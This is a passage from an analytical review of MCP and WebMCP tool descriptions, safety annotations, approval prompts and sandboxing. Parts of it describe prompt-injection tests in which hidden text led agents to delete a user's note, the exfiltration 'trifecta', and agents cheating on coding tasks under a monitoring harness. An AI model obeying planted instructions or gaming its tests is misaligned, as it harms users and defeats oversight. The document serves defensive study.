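The bottom two levels contain 1,393 servers, or 13.6 per cent. This is close to the corrected 13 per cent for DCIChecker, but the agreement is a coincidence, because MCPDiff's figure is a share of servers rather than tools and does not cover overclaiming, the largest group in the DCIChecker survey. Li and colleagues report no manual check of MCPDiff's accuracy, so its figure can't be corrected in the same way.

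The README is an imperfect stand-in for what an agent reads. One of the paper's examples is `longport-mcp`, a server for a share-trading service, whose documents leave out the functions `submit_order` and `cancel_order`. This omission could badly mislead a person who reads the README and then connects her brokerage account. But if the server offers `submit_order` as a tool, the agent sees that name in the tool list and has a good idea of what the tool does.

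MCPDiff starts from every function that no other function calls, so it can include functions that are not tools. `mcpx-py` has an undocumented function, `killtree`, that can stop any program on the computer. This is dangerous if an agent can call it, but much less so if it is unused leftover code.

More popular servers were less likely to have descriptions that fully matched their code. The rate was 53.5 per cent for servers with fewer than ten GitHub stars and 29.1 per cent for those with 1,000 to 9,999. Popular servers probably have more features that a description could omit. A server's popularity therefore doesn't mean that its documentation is complete.

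### Why surveys disagree

Published estimates of the share of tool descriptions that are wrong range from about a tenth to two thirds. Much of the difference comes from what each survey counts.

| Detector | What it examined | What counts as a mismatch | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| SkillScope | 4,556 skills with code | Security-related behavior beyond the description | 9.4% of skills |
| DCIChecker | 17,030 MCP tools | Different functionality, or undisclosed effects | 11.2% of tools, or about 13% after correction |
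| MCPDiff | 10,240 MCP servers | More than a fifth of the code's features missing from the documents | 13.6% of servers |
| SkillAudit | 488 skills from GitHub | Conflicts among documents, code and the software they need | 67.4% of skills |

The last row is from Fan, Wang and colleagues (2026), *Why Static Skill Inconsistencies Do Not Equate to Runtime Risks*. Their definition is much wider than the others and includes, for example, a skill whose documents name version 6 of a charting library in one place and version 7.9.0 in another. Only about a third of the 1,022 faults they found in the GitHub skills were conflicts between documents and code.

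Fan and colleagues also tested how much these faults matter. They built 49 tasks, each leading the agent towards one real fault, and ran three models with the original skill and with a version that repaired only that fault. They scored the agent's work by the share of automatic checks it passed.

| Model | Original skill | Repaired skill | Runs in which the model followed the fault into failure |
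|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.741 | 0.877 | 30% |
| Qwen3.6-35B | 0.707 | 0.792 | 24% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 0.870 | 0.893 | 12% |

The agents read the skill in 97.1 per cent of runs, so the models differed mainly in what they did after reading it. DeepSeek's model often worked around the fault, while the other two were more likely to rely on the text. The number of mismatches is therefore a poor measure of harm, because the same mismatch can stop one agent and barely slow another.

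Overclaiming accounted for the most failures, 41 of the 97 runs in which a model followed a fault and failed. When the documents and the code openly contradicted each other, the models recovered in 13 of 18 runs. An agent can notice a contradiction, but it may not discover that a described feature is missing until the result is wrong. This is a reason to check for overclaiming, which MCPDiff ignores.

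These results probably overstate how often a fault causes trouble in ordinary use, because Fan and colleagues designed each task so that the easiest solution ran into one. But their agents could open the skill's files and repair or avoid the faulty part. An agent that calls a remote tool can't do that, so it might recover less often.

### What the source code leaves out

A checker can find rules in the source code that no trial call has triggered yet, such as a hidden fee on large orders.

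Comparing a tool's description with its source code works only if the checker has the code that will run. Providers of remote servers often keep their code private, and even published code may differ from what the server runs. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) notes that the provider may be running another version, may have put other software in front of the server, or may have changed its settings. The paper cites a May 2026 count of more than 21,000 MCP servers that anyone could reach over the internet.

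Servers also come and go quickly. Padilla confirmed 464 live servers in one round of tests, and 41.6 per cent of them had disappeared by the next round about three days later. Some may only have been offline temporarily. Even so, if a registry checked a server only at publication, its verdict would soon be out of date. The registry could partly solve this by running the servers itself from the code it has checked, but that code might still send data to companies whose code the registry has never seen.

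Some tools fetch part of their code while they run. Shen and colleagues list this among the threats to MCP, because a provider can then change what a tool does without changing the installed package. DCIChecker might list the download, but it couldn't compare the description with code the tool fetches later. Its placeholders are similarly limited, because if a tool works out an address only when it runs, the model can tell that data leaves the computer but not where it goes.

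DCIChecker's survey also covered only Python, which Shi and colleagues put at nearly 40 per cent of working MCP servers. That excludes the `postmark-mcp` package, which was in the JavaScript registry npm, and any WebMCP tool, because web pages register those in JavaScript. MCPDiff handles several languages. The 13 per cent estimate may not apply to servers in other languages, whose programmers may have different habits. Python's docstrings, for instance, make it unusually easy to publish a description by accident.

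A dishonest provider can study the checker and write code to get past it. *SkillProbe* (2026) observes that methods for comparing code with documents have generally assumed that the documents were written in good faith. DCIChecker's limits are public, so a provider could put an upload one layer deeper than the checker reads. The checker's list of benign libraries includes `pickle`, which Python programs use to save and load data, even though Python's documentation warns that loading a malicious `pickle` file can run any code.

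The provider can also try to manipulate the model that checks the code. A false comment in the code may lead the model to treat an upload as only a local backup. The provider could also plant instructions to the model in the code, much as in tool poisoning. Shi and colleagues' test sets weren't designed to include such code, so their error rates apply to mismatches that nobody was trying to hide.

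DCIChecker's list of sensitive calls offers some protection against false comments, because fixed rules produce the list and a comment can't remove a network call from it. A registry could also strip the comments before the model reads the code. But accurate comments help a model understand what code is for, so the registry would first need to test how many additional accurately described tools it would reject without them.

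## Declared annotations such as "read-only" and "destructive"

When a provider keeps its code private, a host cannot check a tool's description against the code, but it can still ask the provider to state the tool's main effects in a fixed form. A label such as `readOnlyHint: true` is less ambiguous than a phrase such as "finalizes the cart", and a program can act on it more easily. But the provider also writes the label, and MCP has no step that checks it against the code.

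### MCP's four hints

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has had annotations since March 2025. Apart from a display title, there are four, and each is a yes-or-no claim about the tool's behavior. The definitions and defaults below come from MCP's *Class ToolAnnotations*, a reference page for programmers. The uses in the last column come from a March 2026 post on the MCP blog.

| Hint | Meaning if true | Assumed if missing | How a host might use it |
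|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool reads data and changes nothing | False | Skip the confirmation prompt if true |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may delete or overwrite things, not just add them | True | Show a warning if true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | False | Retry a failed call if true |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool deals with an unpredictable range of outside parties, as a web search does | True | Treat the results with more suspicion if true |

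The defaults are cautious. A host that follows them treats an unlabelled weather tool as one that might delete data and might do more harm if called again, so a missing label never removes a safeguard. To remove one, the provider has to make a positive claim. If that claim is false, the provider can't excuse it as an oversight the way it could excuse a blank field.

The strict definition of "read-only" allows a tool no side effects except using computing resources, and the tool can't create, update or delete data "in any system". Read literally, this excludes the tool that looks up a user's profile and updates the "last access" time, as well as a weather tool whose server logs each query. The web's standard for GET requests is more relaxed about logs. Many honest providers would label both tools read-only, and most users wouldn't mind. Anyone counting false labels therefore needs the same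 materiality test that applies to descriptions.

"Destructive" covers less than a user might expect, because a tool that only adds things counts as non-destructive. The blog post advises providers to label such tools `destructiveHint: false`. If "finalizeCart" places an order, it adds an order and arguably destroys nothing, so a shop could follow the advice and still charge a shopper $200 she didn't mean to spend. Sending an email also adds something, a message that nobody can take back.

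None of the hints covers what happens to the user's data. The email tool in `postmark-mcp` could have had accurate labels both before and after its developer added the line that copied every message, because both versions changed something and interacted with the outside world, as an email tool should.

### WebMCP's hints

WebMCP also has a `readOnlyHint`, which Chromium (2026), the open-source project behind Chrome, defines as a hint that the tool doesn't modify any state. Another WebMCP hint, `untrustedContentHint`, is for tools whose results may include text from strangers, such as customer reviews. A shop that adds this hint to its review tool warns the agent that somebody may have planted instructions in the results.

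With the untrusted-content hint, unlike the read-only hint, the dangerous mistake is leaving it out, because the agent may then trust a review it should have treated with suspicion. A shop that wanted to manipulate agents would leave it out. Chrome for Developers therefore advises agent makers to treat everything a WebMCP tool returns as untrusted, and to have their models recognize the hint as well. The agent is then careful by default, and the hint can only make it more so.

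A later version of Google's advice, from September 2026, includes the hint for serious actions that the WebMCP group had been planning. Chrome for Developers (2026) recommends `consequentialHint: true` for tools that, for example, book travel or transfer money, so that the agent or browser can ask the user first. This hint suits "finalizeCart" much better than "destructive" does. The same page warns that even a read-only tool, such as one called `getFavoriteProducts`, can reveal private information. It advises sites to offer such a tool only to other sites with which they would share that data directly.

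### The dispute over untrusted labels

MCP's designers disagreed about the value of these labels from the start. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, thought the information would be very useful if hosts could trust it, but he wondered "how a client makes use of this flag knowing that it's not trustable". Basil Hosmer, another participant in the review, argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even the title.

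As a compromise, the specification calls every annotation a hint, requires clients to treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, and lets each client decide how much weight to give them.

This works well when the host has a separate reason to trust the provider. A company that runs its own MCP servers can let its agents call read-only tools without asking, because its own staff wrote the labels and are accountable for mistakes. It works badly when the trust has no basis. According to Model Context Protocol, most clients treat installing a server as a sign that the user trusts it, which would mean that everyone who installed `postmark-mcp` trusted its labels.

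A post on the Model Context Protocol blog distinguishes hints from contracts. A hint helps a host make a decision and is still useful if some providers get it wrong. A contract is a guarantee, so something other than the provider's word has to enforce it. For example, the label `readOnlyHint: true` on a database tool is a hint. If the user connects the tool to a database account without write permission, the database will refuse any change, regardless of the label. The post recommends asking whether each proposed annotation is useful only if it is true. If so, it belongs in the software that controls access or runs the tool.

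That test is demanding, and the existing read-only hint arguably fails it. Its main use is to let a host skip a confirmation prompt, which is a good idea only if the label is true. The post itself accepts that a host can't act on a read-only label from an untrusted server.

Even true labels can mislead a host that looks at one tool at a time. The post's example is a tool called `search_emails`, which may be harmless by itself. But if the agent also has tools that read web pages and send messages, an attacker who controls a page it reads could plant instructions to find private emails and send them out. Willison calls this combination of private data, untrusted content and outside communication the "lethal trifecta". A host can use labels to detect that a session has all three, but only if the labels cover each of them, and MCP has no hint for private data.

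### Proposals for more labels

In March 2026 there were five open proposals for labels to fill such gaps, including a `secretHint`, an `unsafeOutputHint`, and a scheme from GitHub and OpenAI staff for marking how sensitive and trustworthy data is. A month later the project set up an interest group to consider them together. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter*, the group can make recommendations but can't change the specification.

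None of these proposals was listed as accepted or final on Model Context Protocol's list in late November 2026. The project has moved its next release from December to 30 March 2027, according to its roadmap, so the four original hints will probably remain the only standard ones until at least then.

One of the drafts, *SEP-1862* (SamMorrowDrums, 2025), would make labels depend on the arguments of a call. A single tool called `manage_files` might read, rename or delete files. Its provider has to label it destructive because some calls delete files, so a cautious host asks the user to confirm even a call that only reads. The proposal would let the host send the server the intended arguments before the call and receive labels for that call alone. If the action is "read", the server can reply that the call is read-only.

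For an honest provider, this would remove many pointless prompts. It would not make the labels more trustworthy, since the provider's code would also generate the new ones. Like a preview, it would also disclose the arguments to the server before the user had approved anything.

### Why the direction of an error matters

A false "read-only" label does much more harm than a false "destructive" label. If a provider labels a purchase tool read-only, the host may skip the confirmation prompt that would have stopped an unwanted purchase. When a weather tool is labeled destructive, the user may just see a prompt she didn't need.

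Suppose an approval prompt takes 5 cents' worth of the user's attention, and a wrong call costs her $200. Let p be the probability that a read-only label is false, and assume she would stop the wrong call if the host asked her.

```
Cost of asking:                5 cents
Expected cost of not asking:   p × $200

Skipping the prompt pays only if  p × $200 < $0.05
                                  p < 1/4,000
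```

So a host should skip the prompt only if fewer than 1 such label in 4,000 is false. By the rule of three, someone would have to check about 12,000 randomly chosen labels and find no false ones to be 95 per cent confident of a rate that low. I know of no survey close to that size, and a random sample wouldn't protect a user from a provider who targeted her specifically.

The threshold depends on the worst the tool could do. If a wrong call could cost only $2, skipping the prompt would save money on average as long as fewer than 1 label in 40 was false. A host can therefore reasonably accept a read-only label on a tool that can reach only public weather data and reject the same label on one that can reach the user's bank account.

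A user who sees too many needless prompts may switch prompts off. The `manage_files` proposal also argues that models avoid tools labelled destructive. If so, providers lose business by accurately labelling a destructive tool, and a provider who is unsure which label applies has a reason to pick the safer-sounding one.

### How many tools have labels

Most tools have none of the four hints. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) examined a random sample of 400 servers from those in the official registry that come from npm and run on the user's machine. Afsar tried to start each one once, without repairing it or supplying a password. The 195 servers that started offered 2,766 tools, of which 1,626 (58.8 per cent) had no hints.

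On a smaller set of well-known servers that Afsar hand-picked, the figure was 41.5 per cent. The difference suggests that the best-known servers are a poor guide to MCP servers in general. His random sample is also limited, because it leaves out remote servers and Python packages, and the kind of server he tested made up only about 31 per cent of the registry.

Of the servers with at least one tool, 72 had labels on every tool, 122 had no labels, and none had labels on only some tools. This suggests that people decide whether to label tools once for a whole server, perhaps by following a template, rather than tool by tool. A programmer who copies `readOnlyHint: true` from one tool to the next could easily attach it to one that writes.

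Shi and colleagues at Tongji University found even fewer labels. In their sample of 100 popular GitHub servers, 325 of 1,856 tools (17.5 per cent) had annotations. The two results needn't conflict, because if servers label either all of their tools or none, one large server can shift the total a lot, and the largest in Afsar's sample had 300 tools. Neither study's count measures how many of the labels were true.

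### What happens when an agent calls a destructive tool

*When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) provides the most detailed evidence on whether labels and prompts protect users. It studies both the servers that offer destructive tools and the hosts that call them. Its definition of "destructive" is broader than MCP's and includes any tool that could, in some call, irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send a message, move money or run arbitrary commands.

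They assumed that servers and hosts were honest, and that the danger came from a model that misread its task or followed planted instructions. Their results therefore show how well the safeguards work when nobody lies about a tool.

To study servers, the researchers took 1,000 code repositories from the official registry, including the 200 with the most GitHub stars and 800 drawn at random from the rest. A program searched the code and found 16,711 tools. It flagged 1,995 as possibly destructive, mostly from clues such as the word "delete" in a name. The researchers excluded 100 of these, which they had used to develop the program, and drew a sample of 366 from the rest.

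Two language models, GPT-6.1 Sol and Gemini 4 Argon, then separately read the code for each of the 366 tools and classified the tool. Claude Opus 5.5 settled their disagreements, and the final count was 269 destructive tools. Two people also classified 60 of the tools without seeing the models' answers. They agreed with the models on how 58 of the 60 handled confirmation. They agreed with the models less often on which tools were destructive. In every such disagreement, the models had classified a tool as destructive for an action that the people considered reversible or harmless, such as renaming a project.

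The program had missed most destructive tools. In 40 repositories that the researchers examined in full, it had missed 265 of the 319 destructive tools. The estimates below correct for these omissions.

| What the server does before a destructive call | Share of destructive tools |
|---|---|
| Nothing, and the tool has no destructive label | 70% |
| Nothing, but the tool has a destructive label | 20% |
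| Requires a confirmation that the model can supply itself | 8.9% |
| Asks the user if the host can pass on the question, and otherwise goes ahead | 0.2% |
| Refuses unless a person has answered | 0.5% |

The top two rows together make up about 90 per cent, with a 95 per cent confidence interval from 82 to 95. The split between them is much less certain.

A confirmation that the model can supply, usually as an extra argument such as `confirm=true`, offers little protection. Yao and colleagues built a test server with a tool for deleting notes, and in its list of notes they hid an instruction to delete one that the user wanted to keep. Even when the hidden text didn't mention the argument, the models set it and deleted the note in 127 of 169 attempts. Over the whole experiment, four of the five low-cost models deleted the wrong note in 479 of 960 runs, while the fifth, from DeepSeek, never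 deleted it.

The researchers chose 41 popular open-source hosts, made up of 25 applications and 16 software kits for building agents. AI agents traced how each host's code handled an ordinary tool call under default settings. Seven hosts, including VS Code and Gemini CLI, prompted the user for approval. Codex CLI decided based on the tool's labels, and Qwen Code used a language model to decide. The other 32, including every software kit, had no approval step. Adding a destructive label to a tool changed nothing on 39 of the 41 hosts, because they either prompted anyway or never prompted.

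Servers and host applications each seem to leave it to the other to confirm destructive actions. One server for the mapping program QGIS skips its own confirmation by default "because MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves". Another server requests confirmation before deleting a database, but deletes it anyway if the host application can't pass the request to the user. Cline and LibreChat neither pass on such requests nor prompt the user themselves, so in either application the server would delete the database without anyone's approval.

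### Tools and hosts combined

Yao and colleagues then paired each of the 269 destructive tools with each host and worked out whether a person would have to approve the call. They weighted the tools to reflect how they had drawn the sample. They also estimated what would happen if hosts or servers behaved differently.

| What hosts and servers do | No enforced approval, 25 applications | No enforced approval, all 41 hosts | Needless prompts, 25 applications |
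|---|---|---|---|
| Current defaults | 60.7% | 74.9% | 32.5% |
| Every host passes on servers' questions | 56.7% | 69.1% | 35.2% |
| Every host prompts unless the tool is labelled read-only or non-destructive | 5.4% | 5.4% | 82.6% |
| The same, after adding the tools that the program missed | Not reported | At least 10.6% | Not reported |
| Every destructive tool refuses unless a person has answered | 0% | 0% | 32.5% |

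The last column gives the share of pairs in which the user would get a prompt for a tool that the program had flagged but the models judged harmless.

The 60.7 per cent is a share of pairs, and every application counts equally however many users it has, so it isn't the chance that a typical user's agent deletes something without asking. The figure also depends heavily on which applications are included, since 16 of the 25 have no approval step. It fell to 47.5 per cent when the researchers added seven closed-source applications, including Claude Code and Cursor, relying on documentation for those seven.

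Passing on servers' questions would barely help, because so few servers send any. Making every destructive tool refuse would remove all the unapproved calls, but most tools would stop working. In 71 per cent of application pairs, the server would refuse because the host couldn't pass on its question. Some of those refusals would be needless, since the user would already have approved the call in the host's own prompt, which the server can't detect. Yao and colleagues suggest that hosts could declare to servers that they obtain human approval. That might work, but servers would have to trust a label written by the host.

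The best of these options is to prompt unless the provider has labelled the tool safe, which is close to what MCP's cautious defaults already imply. However, this raises needless prompts for applications from 32.5 to 82.6 per cent of pairs. Those percentages probably understate the problem, because they leave out ordinary look-up tools that the program never flagged, such as `get_weather`. More than half of all tools in Afsar's sample would trigger a prompt simply because they have no labels.

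### Destructive tools with a safe label

If every host followed that rule, the only destructive calls to run without approval would be to tools that providers had labelled read-only or non-destructive. The host's own default would no longer matter, so the figure is the same for applications and for all hosts, at 5.4 per cent of pairs. That is about 1 in 19 of the flagged destructive tools. Adding the tools that the program missed raises this to at least 1 in 10. It could be higher, because the researchers assumed that any tool their program had failed to extract had no label.

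Some of these labels may be honest and even correct. A provider who labels an email tool non-destructive is following MCP's definition, although Yao and colleagues count sending a message as destructive. The models also tended to count reversible actions as destructive, which will have added a few more such labels. An honest label still doesn't protect the user, because the host sends the email without prompting them first.

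The results also give a rough idea of how strong a safe label is as evidence. Under the proposed rule, a safe label would remove the prompt for about 17 per cent of the flagged tools that turned out to be harmless and about 5 per cent of those that turned out to be destructive. Safe labels were therefore only about three times as common on the harmless tools as on the destructive ones. If 7 in 10 tools with destructive-sounding names are destructive, roughly the proportion in the sample, a safe label on one of them would lower the chance that it is destructive to about 42 per cent, which is still far above 1 in 4,000.

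A read-only label is much more likely to be true for a tool with a name like `get_weather`, but mostly because of the name. A host could therefore prompt the user whenever a tool's name and label disagree. That would catch many careless providers, but a dishonest one could choose a milder name.

The 5.4 per cent would probably not last if hosts adopted the rule. Providers wrote today's labels when most hosts ignored them, so a false label gained them little. If a safe label meant fewer prompts, a provider whose tool kept triggering them would have a good reason to add one. Yao and colleagues point out that hosts could instead skip the prompt only for tools labelled read-only. This would catch false claims that a tool is non-destructive, but it would produce still more prompts. Codex CLI takes a middle course and skips the prompt for a non-destructive tool only if its provider has also labelled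 it closed to the outside world.

### What a person can approve

Yao and colleagues recorded whether a person had to decide before a call ran, not whether the person read the prompt or understood it.

User approval works best when the agent is doing the wrong thing and the tool's description is accurate. In the test with the notes, a prompt that named the note about to be deleted would have given the user an excellent chance to refuse, because she would have known that she never asked to delete it.

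Asking the user to approve a call works much less well when the tool's description is false, because the user reads the same description as the agent. If a shop's `show_cart` tool actually places an order, a shopper who has just asked to see her cart will probably approve the call.

This also changes the earlier calculation, which assumed that the user stops every wrong call. If she stops only one in ten, skipping the prompt saves money on average as long as fewer than 1 label in 400 is false. If she would never notice a false label, the prompt wastes 5 cents, and something other than her approval has to protect her.

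Experience with web browsers suggests that people heed some warnings, depending on their design. In *Alice in Warningland*, Akhawe and Felt (2013) studied more than 25 million security warnings in Chrome and Firefox. Users clicked through fewer than a quarter of the malware and phishing warnings in either browser, but about 70 per cent of Chrome's warnings about faulty security certificates. These warnings had an important advantage over a prompt that repeats a tool's name, because the browser checked the site itself instead of relying on the word of the party whose honesty is in question.

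A host can improve its approval prompts by including facts it can check itself, such as the server's address, the exact arguments, and whether the provider changed the description last week. It could also show the annotations, marked as the provider's claims. According to Model Context Protocol, no MCP client showed annotations in its approval prompts in March 2026.

### Who checks the labels

Companies that run tool directories can check labels before users see them. When OpenAI opened ChatGPT's app directory to submissions in December 2025, its guidelines required developers to label read-only, destructive and open-world tools correctly. OpenAI listed wrong or missing labels as a common reason for rejection. Anthropic's directory policy required read-only and destructive hints where they applied, and descriptions that matched what the tools did. Both companies may have changed these rules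 since.

These rules should greatly reduce the number of missing labels, because a reviewer can easily see that a field is blank. False labels are harder to find. Both companies asked developers for a test account with sample data so that a reviewer could try the tools. This testing should catch a "read-only" tool that visibly deletes a record, but it may miss one that keeps a copy of every query on the provider's machine. A dishonest provider also knows which account belongs to the reviewer and can make its tools match their labels on that account.

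OpenAI also locked the names, inputs and descriptions of tools in published apps, so developers had to resubmit an app to change them. This works like a pin that the directory keeps for every user and, like a pin, it doesn't detect changes in a remote server's code.

### What app privacy labels showed

App stores have tried self-declared labels on a large scale. Since December 2020, Apple has required developers to declare what data their apps collect, and it shows their answers to users in a standard format. Apple noted alongside the labels that it hadn't verified them.

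Problems appeared almost immediately. In January 2021 Geoffrey Fowler, a columnist at *The Washington Post*, spot-checked about two dozen apps and found more than a dozen with misleading or inaccurate labels. One was a slime-simulation game labeled as collecting no data, although it sent identifying information to Facebook and other companies.

In *Keeping Privacy Labels Honest*, Koch and colleagues (2022) tested this more systematically by running 1,687 iPhone apps, without tapping anything in them, and recording the data each one sent. At least 276 of the apps (16 per cent) sent data that their privacy labels didn't declare. The real share was probably higher, because many apps send more once somebody starts using them. The researchers concluded that Apple's approval process hadn't checked whether the labels were correct.

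Many of the errors were probably accidental. In *Understanding Challenges for Developers to Create Accurate Privacy Nutrition Labels*, Li and colleagues at Carnegie Mellon University (2022) watched 12 iPhone developers fill in the labels for their own apps. The developers misunderstood some of Apple's definitions and didn't always know what data the third-party code in their apps collected. Some declared too little and others too much. Tool providers are likely to have similar trouble deciding whether sending an email is "destructive" or whether writing a log entry breaks "read-only". Clearer definitions would therefore prevent some false labels, even without any checks.

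The comparison is imperfect, because a privacy label only informs the user, while a tool label may also determine whether the user sees a prompt, so a false one can do more immediate harm. A false tool label can also be harder to expose. Koch and colleagues could watch what left the phone, but users can't watch a remote server in the same way.

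## Observing and restricting a tool while it runs

A host can limit the harm from a false description without knowing that it is false. If a file-search tool has no way to reach the network, it can't upload the user's queries, whatever its provider wrote about it. For a tool on the user's own machine, working out what it could do if its description were false is often easier than checking whether the description is true, because that depends on which files, secrets and network addresses the tool can reach, and the host can control all of these.

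The usual way to control a running tool is a sandbox, an environment that limits and records what a program can read, write and contact. Many MCP servers run without one. Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2025) point out in *AgentBound* that a local server often inherits every permission of the agent that started it. A tool that only needs to look up the weather may therefore be able to read the user's private keys.

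### A permission list for a weather tool

Suppose a user installs a weather tool on her laptop, with the description "Get current weather information for a location". When she asks about Lisbon, the tool's code takes three steps:

1. It sends "Lisbon" to the weather company and gets the forecast.
2. It adds "Lisbon" to a profile file in her home folder.
3. It reports the query to an analytics service.

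The description covers only the forecast. A permission list based on what a forecast requires might look like this, with invented addresses:

```
{
  "network":     ["api.weather.example"],  // may contact only this address
  "environment": ["WEATHER_KEY"],          // may read only this setting
  "read_files":  [],                       // may read none of her files
  "write_files": []                        // may write none of her files
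}
```

A sandbox that enforces this list forbids everything else.

| Effect | Outcome | What the host can record |
|---|---|---|
| The tool sends "Lisbon" to `api.weather.example` | Allowed | The address, time and size of the request |
| The tool writes "Lisbon" to the profile file | Blocked | The attempt and the file's name |
| The tool contacts `stats.example`, the analytics service | Blocked | The attempt and the address |
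| The weather company adds "Lisbon" to a query history on its own server | Beyond the sandbox's reach | Nothing |

The user still gets her forecast if the code keeps running after the two failures. A badly written tool might crash instead, and her legitimate call would fail.

The host can't see the query history because the weather company keeps it outside the sandbox. The company could also pass the query to the analytics service itself, in which case blocking the tool from contacting that service directly would achieve nothing. If the whole tool ran on the company's server, as remote MCP tools do, the host couldn't see the profile or the analytics report either.

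### How a sandbox enforces the list

AgentBound, a system by Bühler and colleagues, borrows the idea of a permission list from Android. It runs each MCP server in a container, which gives a program its own restricted view of the computer. The server starts with no permissions, and the container includes only the folders and settings the user approves. For network access, AgentBound looks up the numerical address of each site the user approves and sets a firewall to drop all other traffic.

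The researchers tested AgentBound on malicious servers from public collections. One, a weather server, swaps the weather company's address for another while it runs. AgentBound blocked the new address and stopped a Google Maps server that used the same trick. It didn't stop a time-zone server whose description contained planted instructions to redirect cryptocurrency payments, because the payments went through a different tool that had permission to make them.

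The sandbox slowed the servers only slightly. The weather server's startup time rose from 554 to 643 milliseconds on a Mac and from 620 to 857 milliseconds on a Linux machine. Once a server was running, common operations such as reading a file took less than a millisecond longer on average.

AgentBound installs the server's package before it turns on the network restrictions, so an install script like the one in `mcp-server-pg` could still contact its author's address. Because the script runs inside the container, it would probably have access to less information to send.

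### Permissions drawn from a false description

A permission list protects the user only if it allows less than a dishonest provider wants. If the provider writes the list, she can add the profile file and the analytics service. This is still better than a description that omits them, because the provider has to ask for the access openly, and a user may wonder why a weather tool needs to write files. But a false description, such as a claim that the tool "remembers your favorite cities", can make the request seem reasonable.

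Requests for broad access won't stand out much. Bühler and colleagues had language models draft lists of the access that 296 popular MCP servers need, based on the servers' code and documents. According to these drafts, 83.1 per cent of the servers need to contact the network, 74.1 per cent to read files and 49.3 per cent to write them.

The researchers report that 80.9 per cent of the drafts were correct, but that figure is based on few replies. They sent drafts to the developers of 96 servers, and their published percentages imply that 17 developers accepted the draft, 4 rejected it, 4 were still discussing it and 71 never answered. In a separate check of 48 servers, 28 drafts matched a list a researcher had written by hand. The other 20 left out 23 permissions and added 6 that the server didn't need. A missing permission blocks legitimate calls until somebody corrects the list, while an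 unnecessary one leaves the tool with access it could misuse.

Matching the code is also the wrong goal for a misrepresented tool. A model that reads the weather tool's code would find the profile file and the analytics service, and might list both as needed. The sandbox would then permit the behavior the provider had hidden. In the test with the malicious weather server, the list came from the harmless original, so it didn't include the swapped address. A tool that was malicious from its first version has no harmless original from which to make such a list.

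Basing the list on the task is safer, since any tool that fetches a forecast needs roughly the same access. A host could start from strict defaults and make the provider justify each exception. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) recommends such defaults: read-only files for the server, a short list of approved addresses, and no access to the passwords and keys on the user's machine.

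### Limits on network destinations

Network limits matter most for a tool that handles private data, because they restrict where the tool can send that data. Chrome for Developers similarly advises makers of browser agents to let an agent interact only with websites relevant to the user's task.

These limits control where a tool sends data but not what it sends. *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026) reports that permission checks on individual calls can't detect sensitive content that travels as an ordinary input to an approved destination. For example, the `postmark-mcp` package had to contact Postmark's service to send any email, and it added the blind-copy recipient to that same message. A list that allowed only Postmark's service would have let every copy through.

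A host could catch the extra recipient only by comparing the outgoing message with the one the agent asked for. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) describes a sandbox that records the requests MCP servers send to outside services, including their inputs. These records could provide the evidence for that comparison. Someone would still have to write a rule for each kind of tool, because an extra recipient is suspicious in an email but an extra field in a weather request may be routine.

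A firewall that filters by IP address can also be too loose or too strict. Many websites often share one address, so a rule that admits the weather company might also admit the analytics service. If the weather company moves to a new address, the rule will block legitimate forecast requests until the host looks the address up again.

### Recording what a call changes

A host can also let a tool run and record its effects. It can fingerprint each file before and after the call and list the files that changed. For other effects, it can log the tool's requests to the operating system, such as requests to open a network connection or start another program.

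*Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) compares two ways to detect risky powers in a server's tools, such as running commands or writing files. The first searches Python code and tool descriptions for words and patterns that suggest these powers. The second runs the server in a container, sends hostile inputs to its tools, and logs its requests to the operating system. On nine deliberately vulnerable servers, the search flagged two and the container test flagged all nine.

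This result doesn't show that running a tool reveals more than reading its code. The search couldn't read JavaScript, and the seven servers it missed were all in JavaScript. It flagged both Python servers. None of the nine servers was safe, so the test can't measure the rate of false alarms. The monitor gave five of the JavaScript servers the same risk score, 60.7 out of 100, although their faults ranged from planted instructions to outdated packages. It may have been mostly detecting something that all of these servers do when they start.

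The auditor is more useful for listing what a tool can do than for detecting bad servers. For the weather tool, it should report that the code writes a file and contacts two addresses. A person could then see that the description accounts for only one of the addresses.

### Checking an agent's own declaration

In *EPISTEME*, Bobadilla, Cesarano and colleagues (2026) automate the comparison between a declaration and its recorded effects, but the declaration comes from the agent rather than the tool's provider.

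EPISTEME is a harness for coding agents, the software that runs their commands. Before each shell command, the agent has to declare one of seven types, such as "collect-info" or "change-state", and give a reason. The harness fingerprints the files in the workspace before and after the command. If the agent declared a read-only type and a file changed, the harness records a contradiction.

The researchers tested EPISTEME on programming tasks that an agent can pass only by cheating, because the tests contradict the instructions. Two models completed 400 runs and cheated in 49 of them. The record showed the cheating in 44 of the 49, but all 44 times the agent had admitted it in its stated reason. One agent wrote that it would replace a formula with a table of the expected answers. The file changes contradicted the agent's declaration in only 3 runs, and the stated reasons had already revealed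 the cheating in all 3.

The comparison found so little partly because it could not detect most of the cheating. In 33 of the 49 runs, the agent used a file-editing tool to tailor its code to the faulty test. EPISTEME assigns a type to those edits automatically, so there was no declaration for the edits to contradict.

An agent declares what it means to do, while a provider describes what the code does. An agent that calls the weather tool from the shell could honestly declare "collect-info", and the change to the profile file would contradict that declaration even though the provider was at fault. A contradiction therefore doesn't show whether the agent was dishonest or deceived. The agents in the experiment were also very candid, whereas a provider who has hidden an analytics service is unlikely to mention it when asked for a reason.

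A host could use the same method to check a provider's read-only label, since any changed file would contradict the label. EPISTEME wouldn't suit the weather tool, because it cuts off the network to keep every lasting effect inside the workspace, and the tool couldn't fetch a forecast.

### Watching tools on a web page

With WebMCP, the browser receives a tool's description and also runs its code, so it can compare the two. *WebMCP-Phalanx* (Lee, Chang and colleagues, 2026) proposes using the browser for this check. While a tool runs, the browser watches for outgoing requests and changes to the page. If these don't fit the tool's declared behavior, the browser changes the tool's trust label to red, and the agent receives the new label with the result. The system can then isolate or block the tool.

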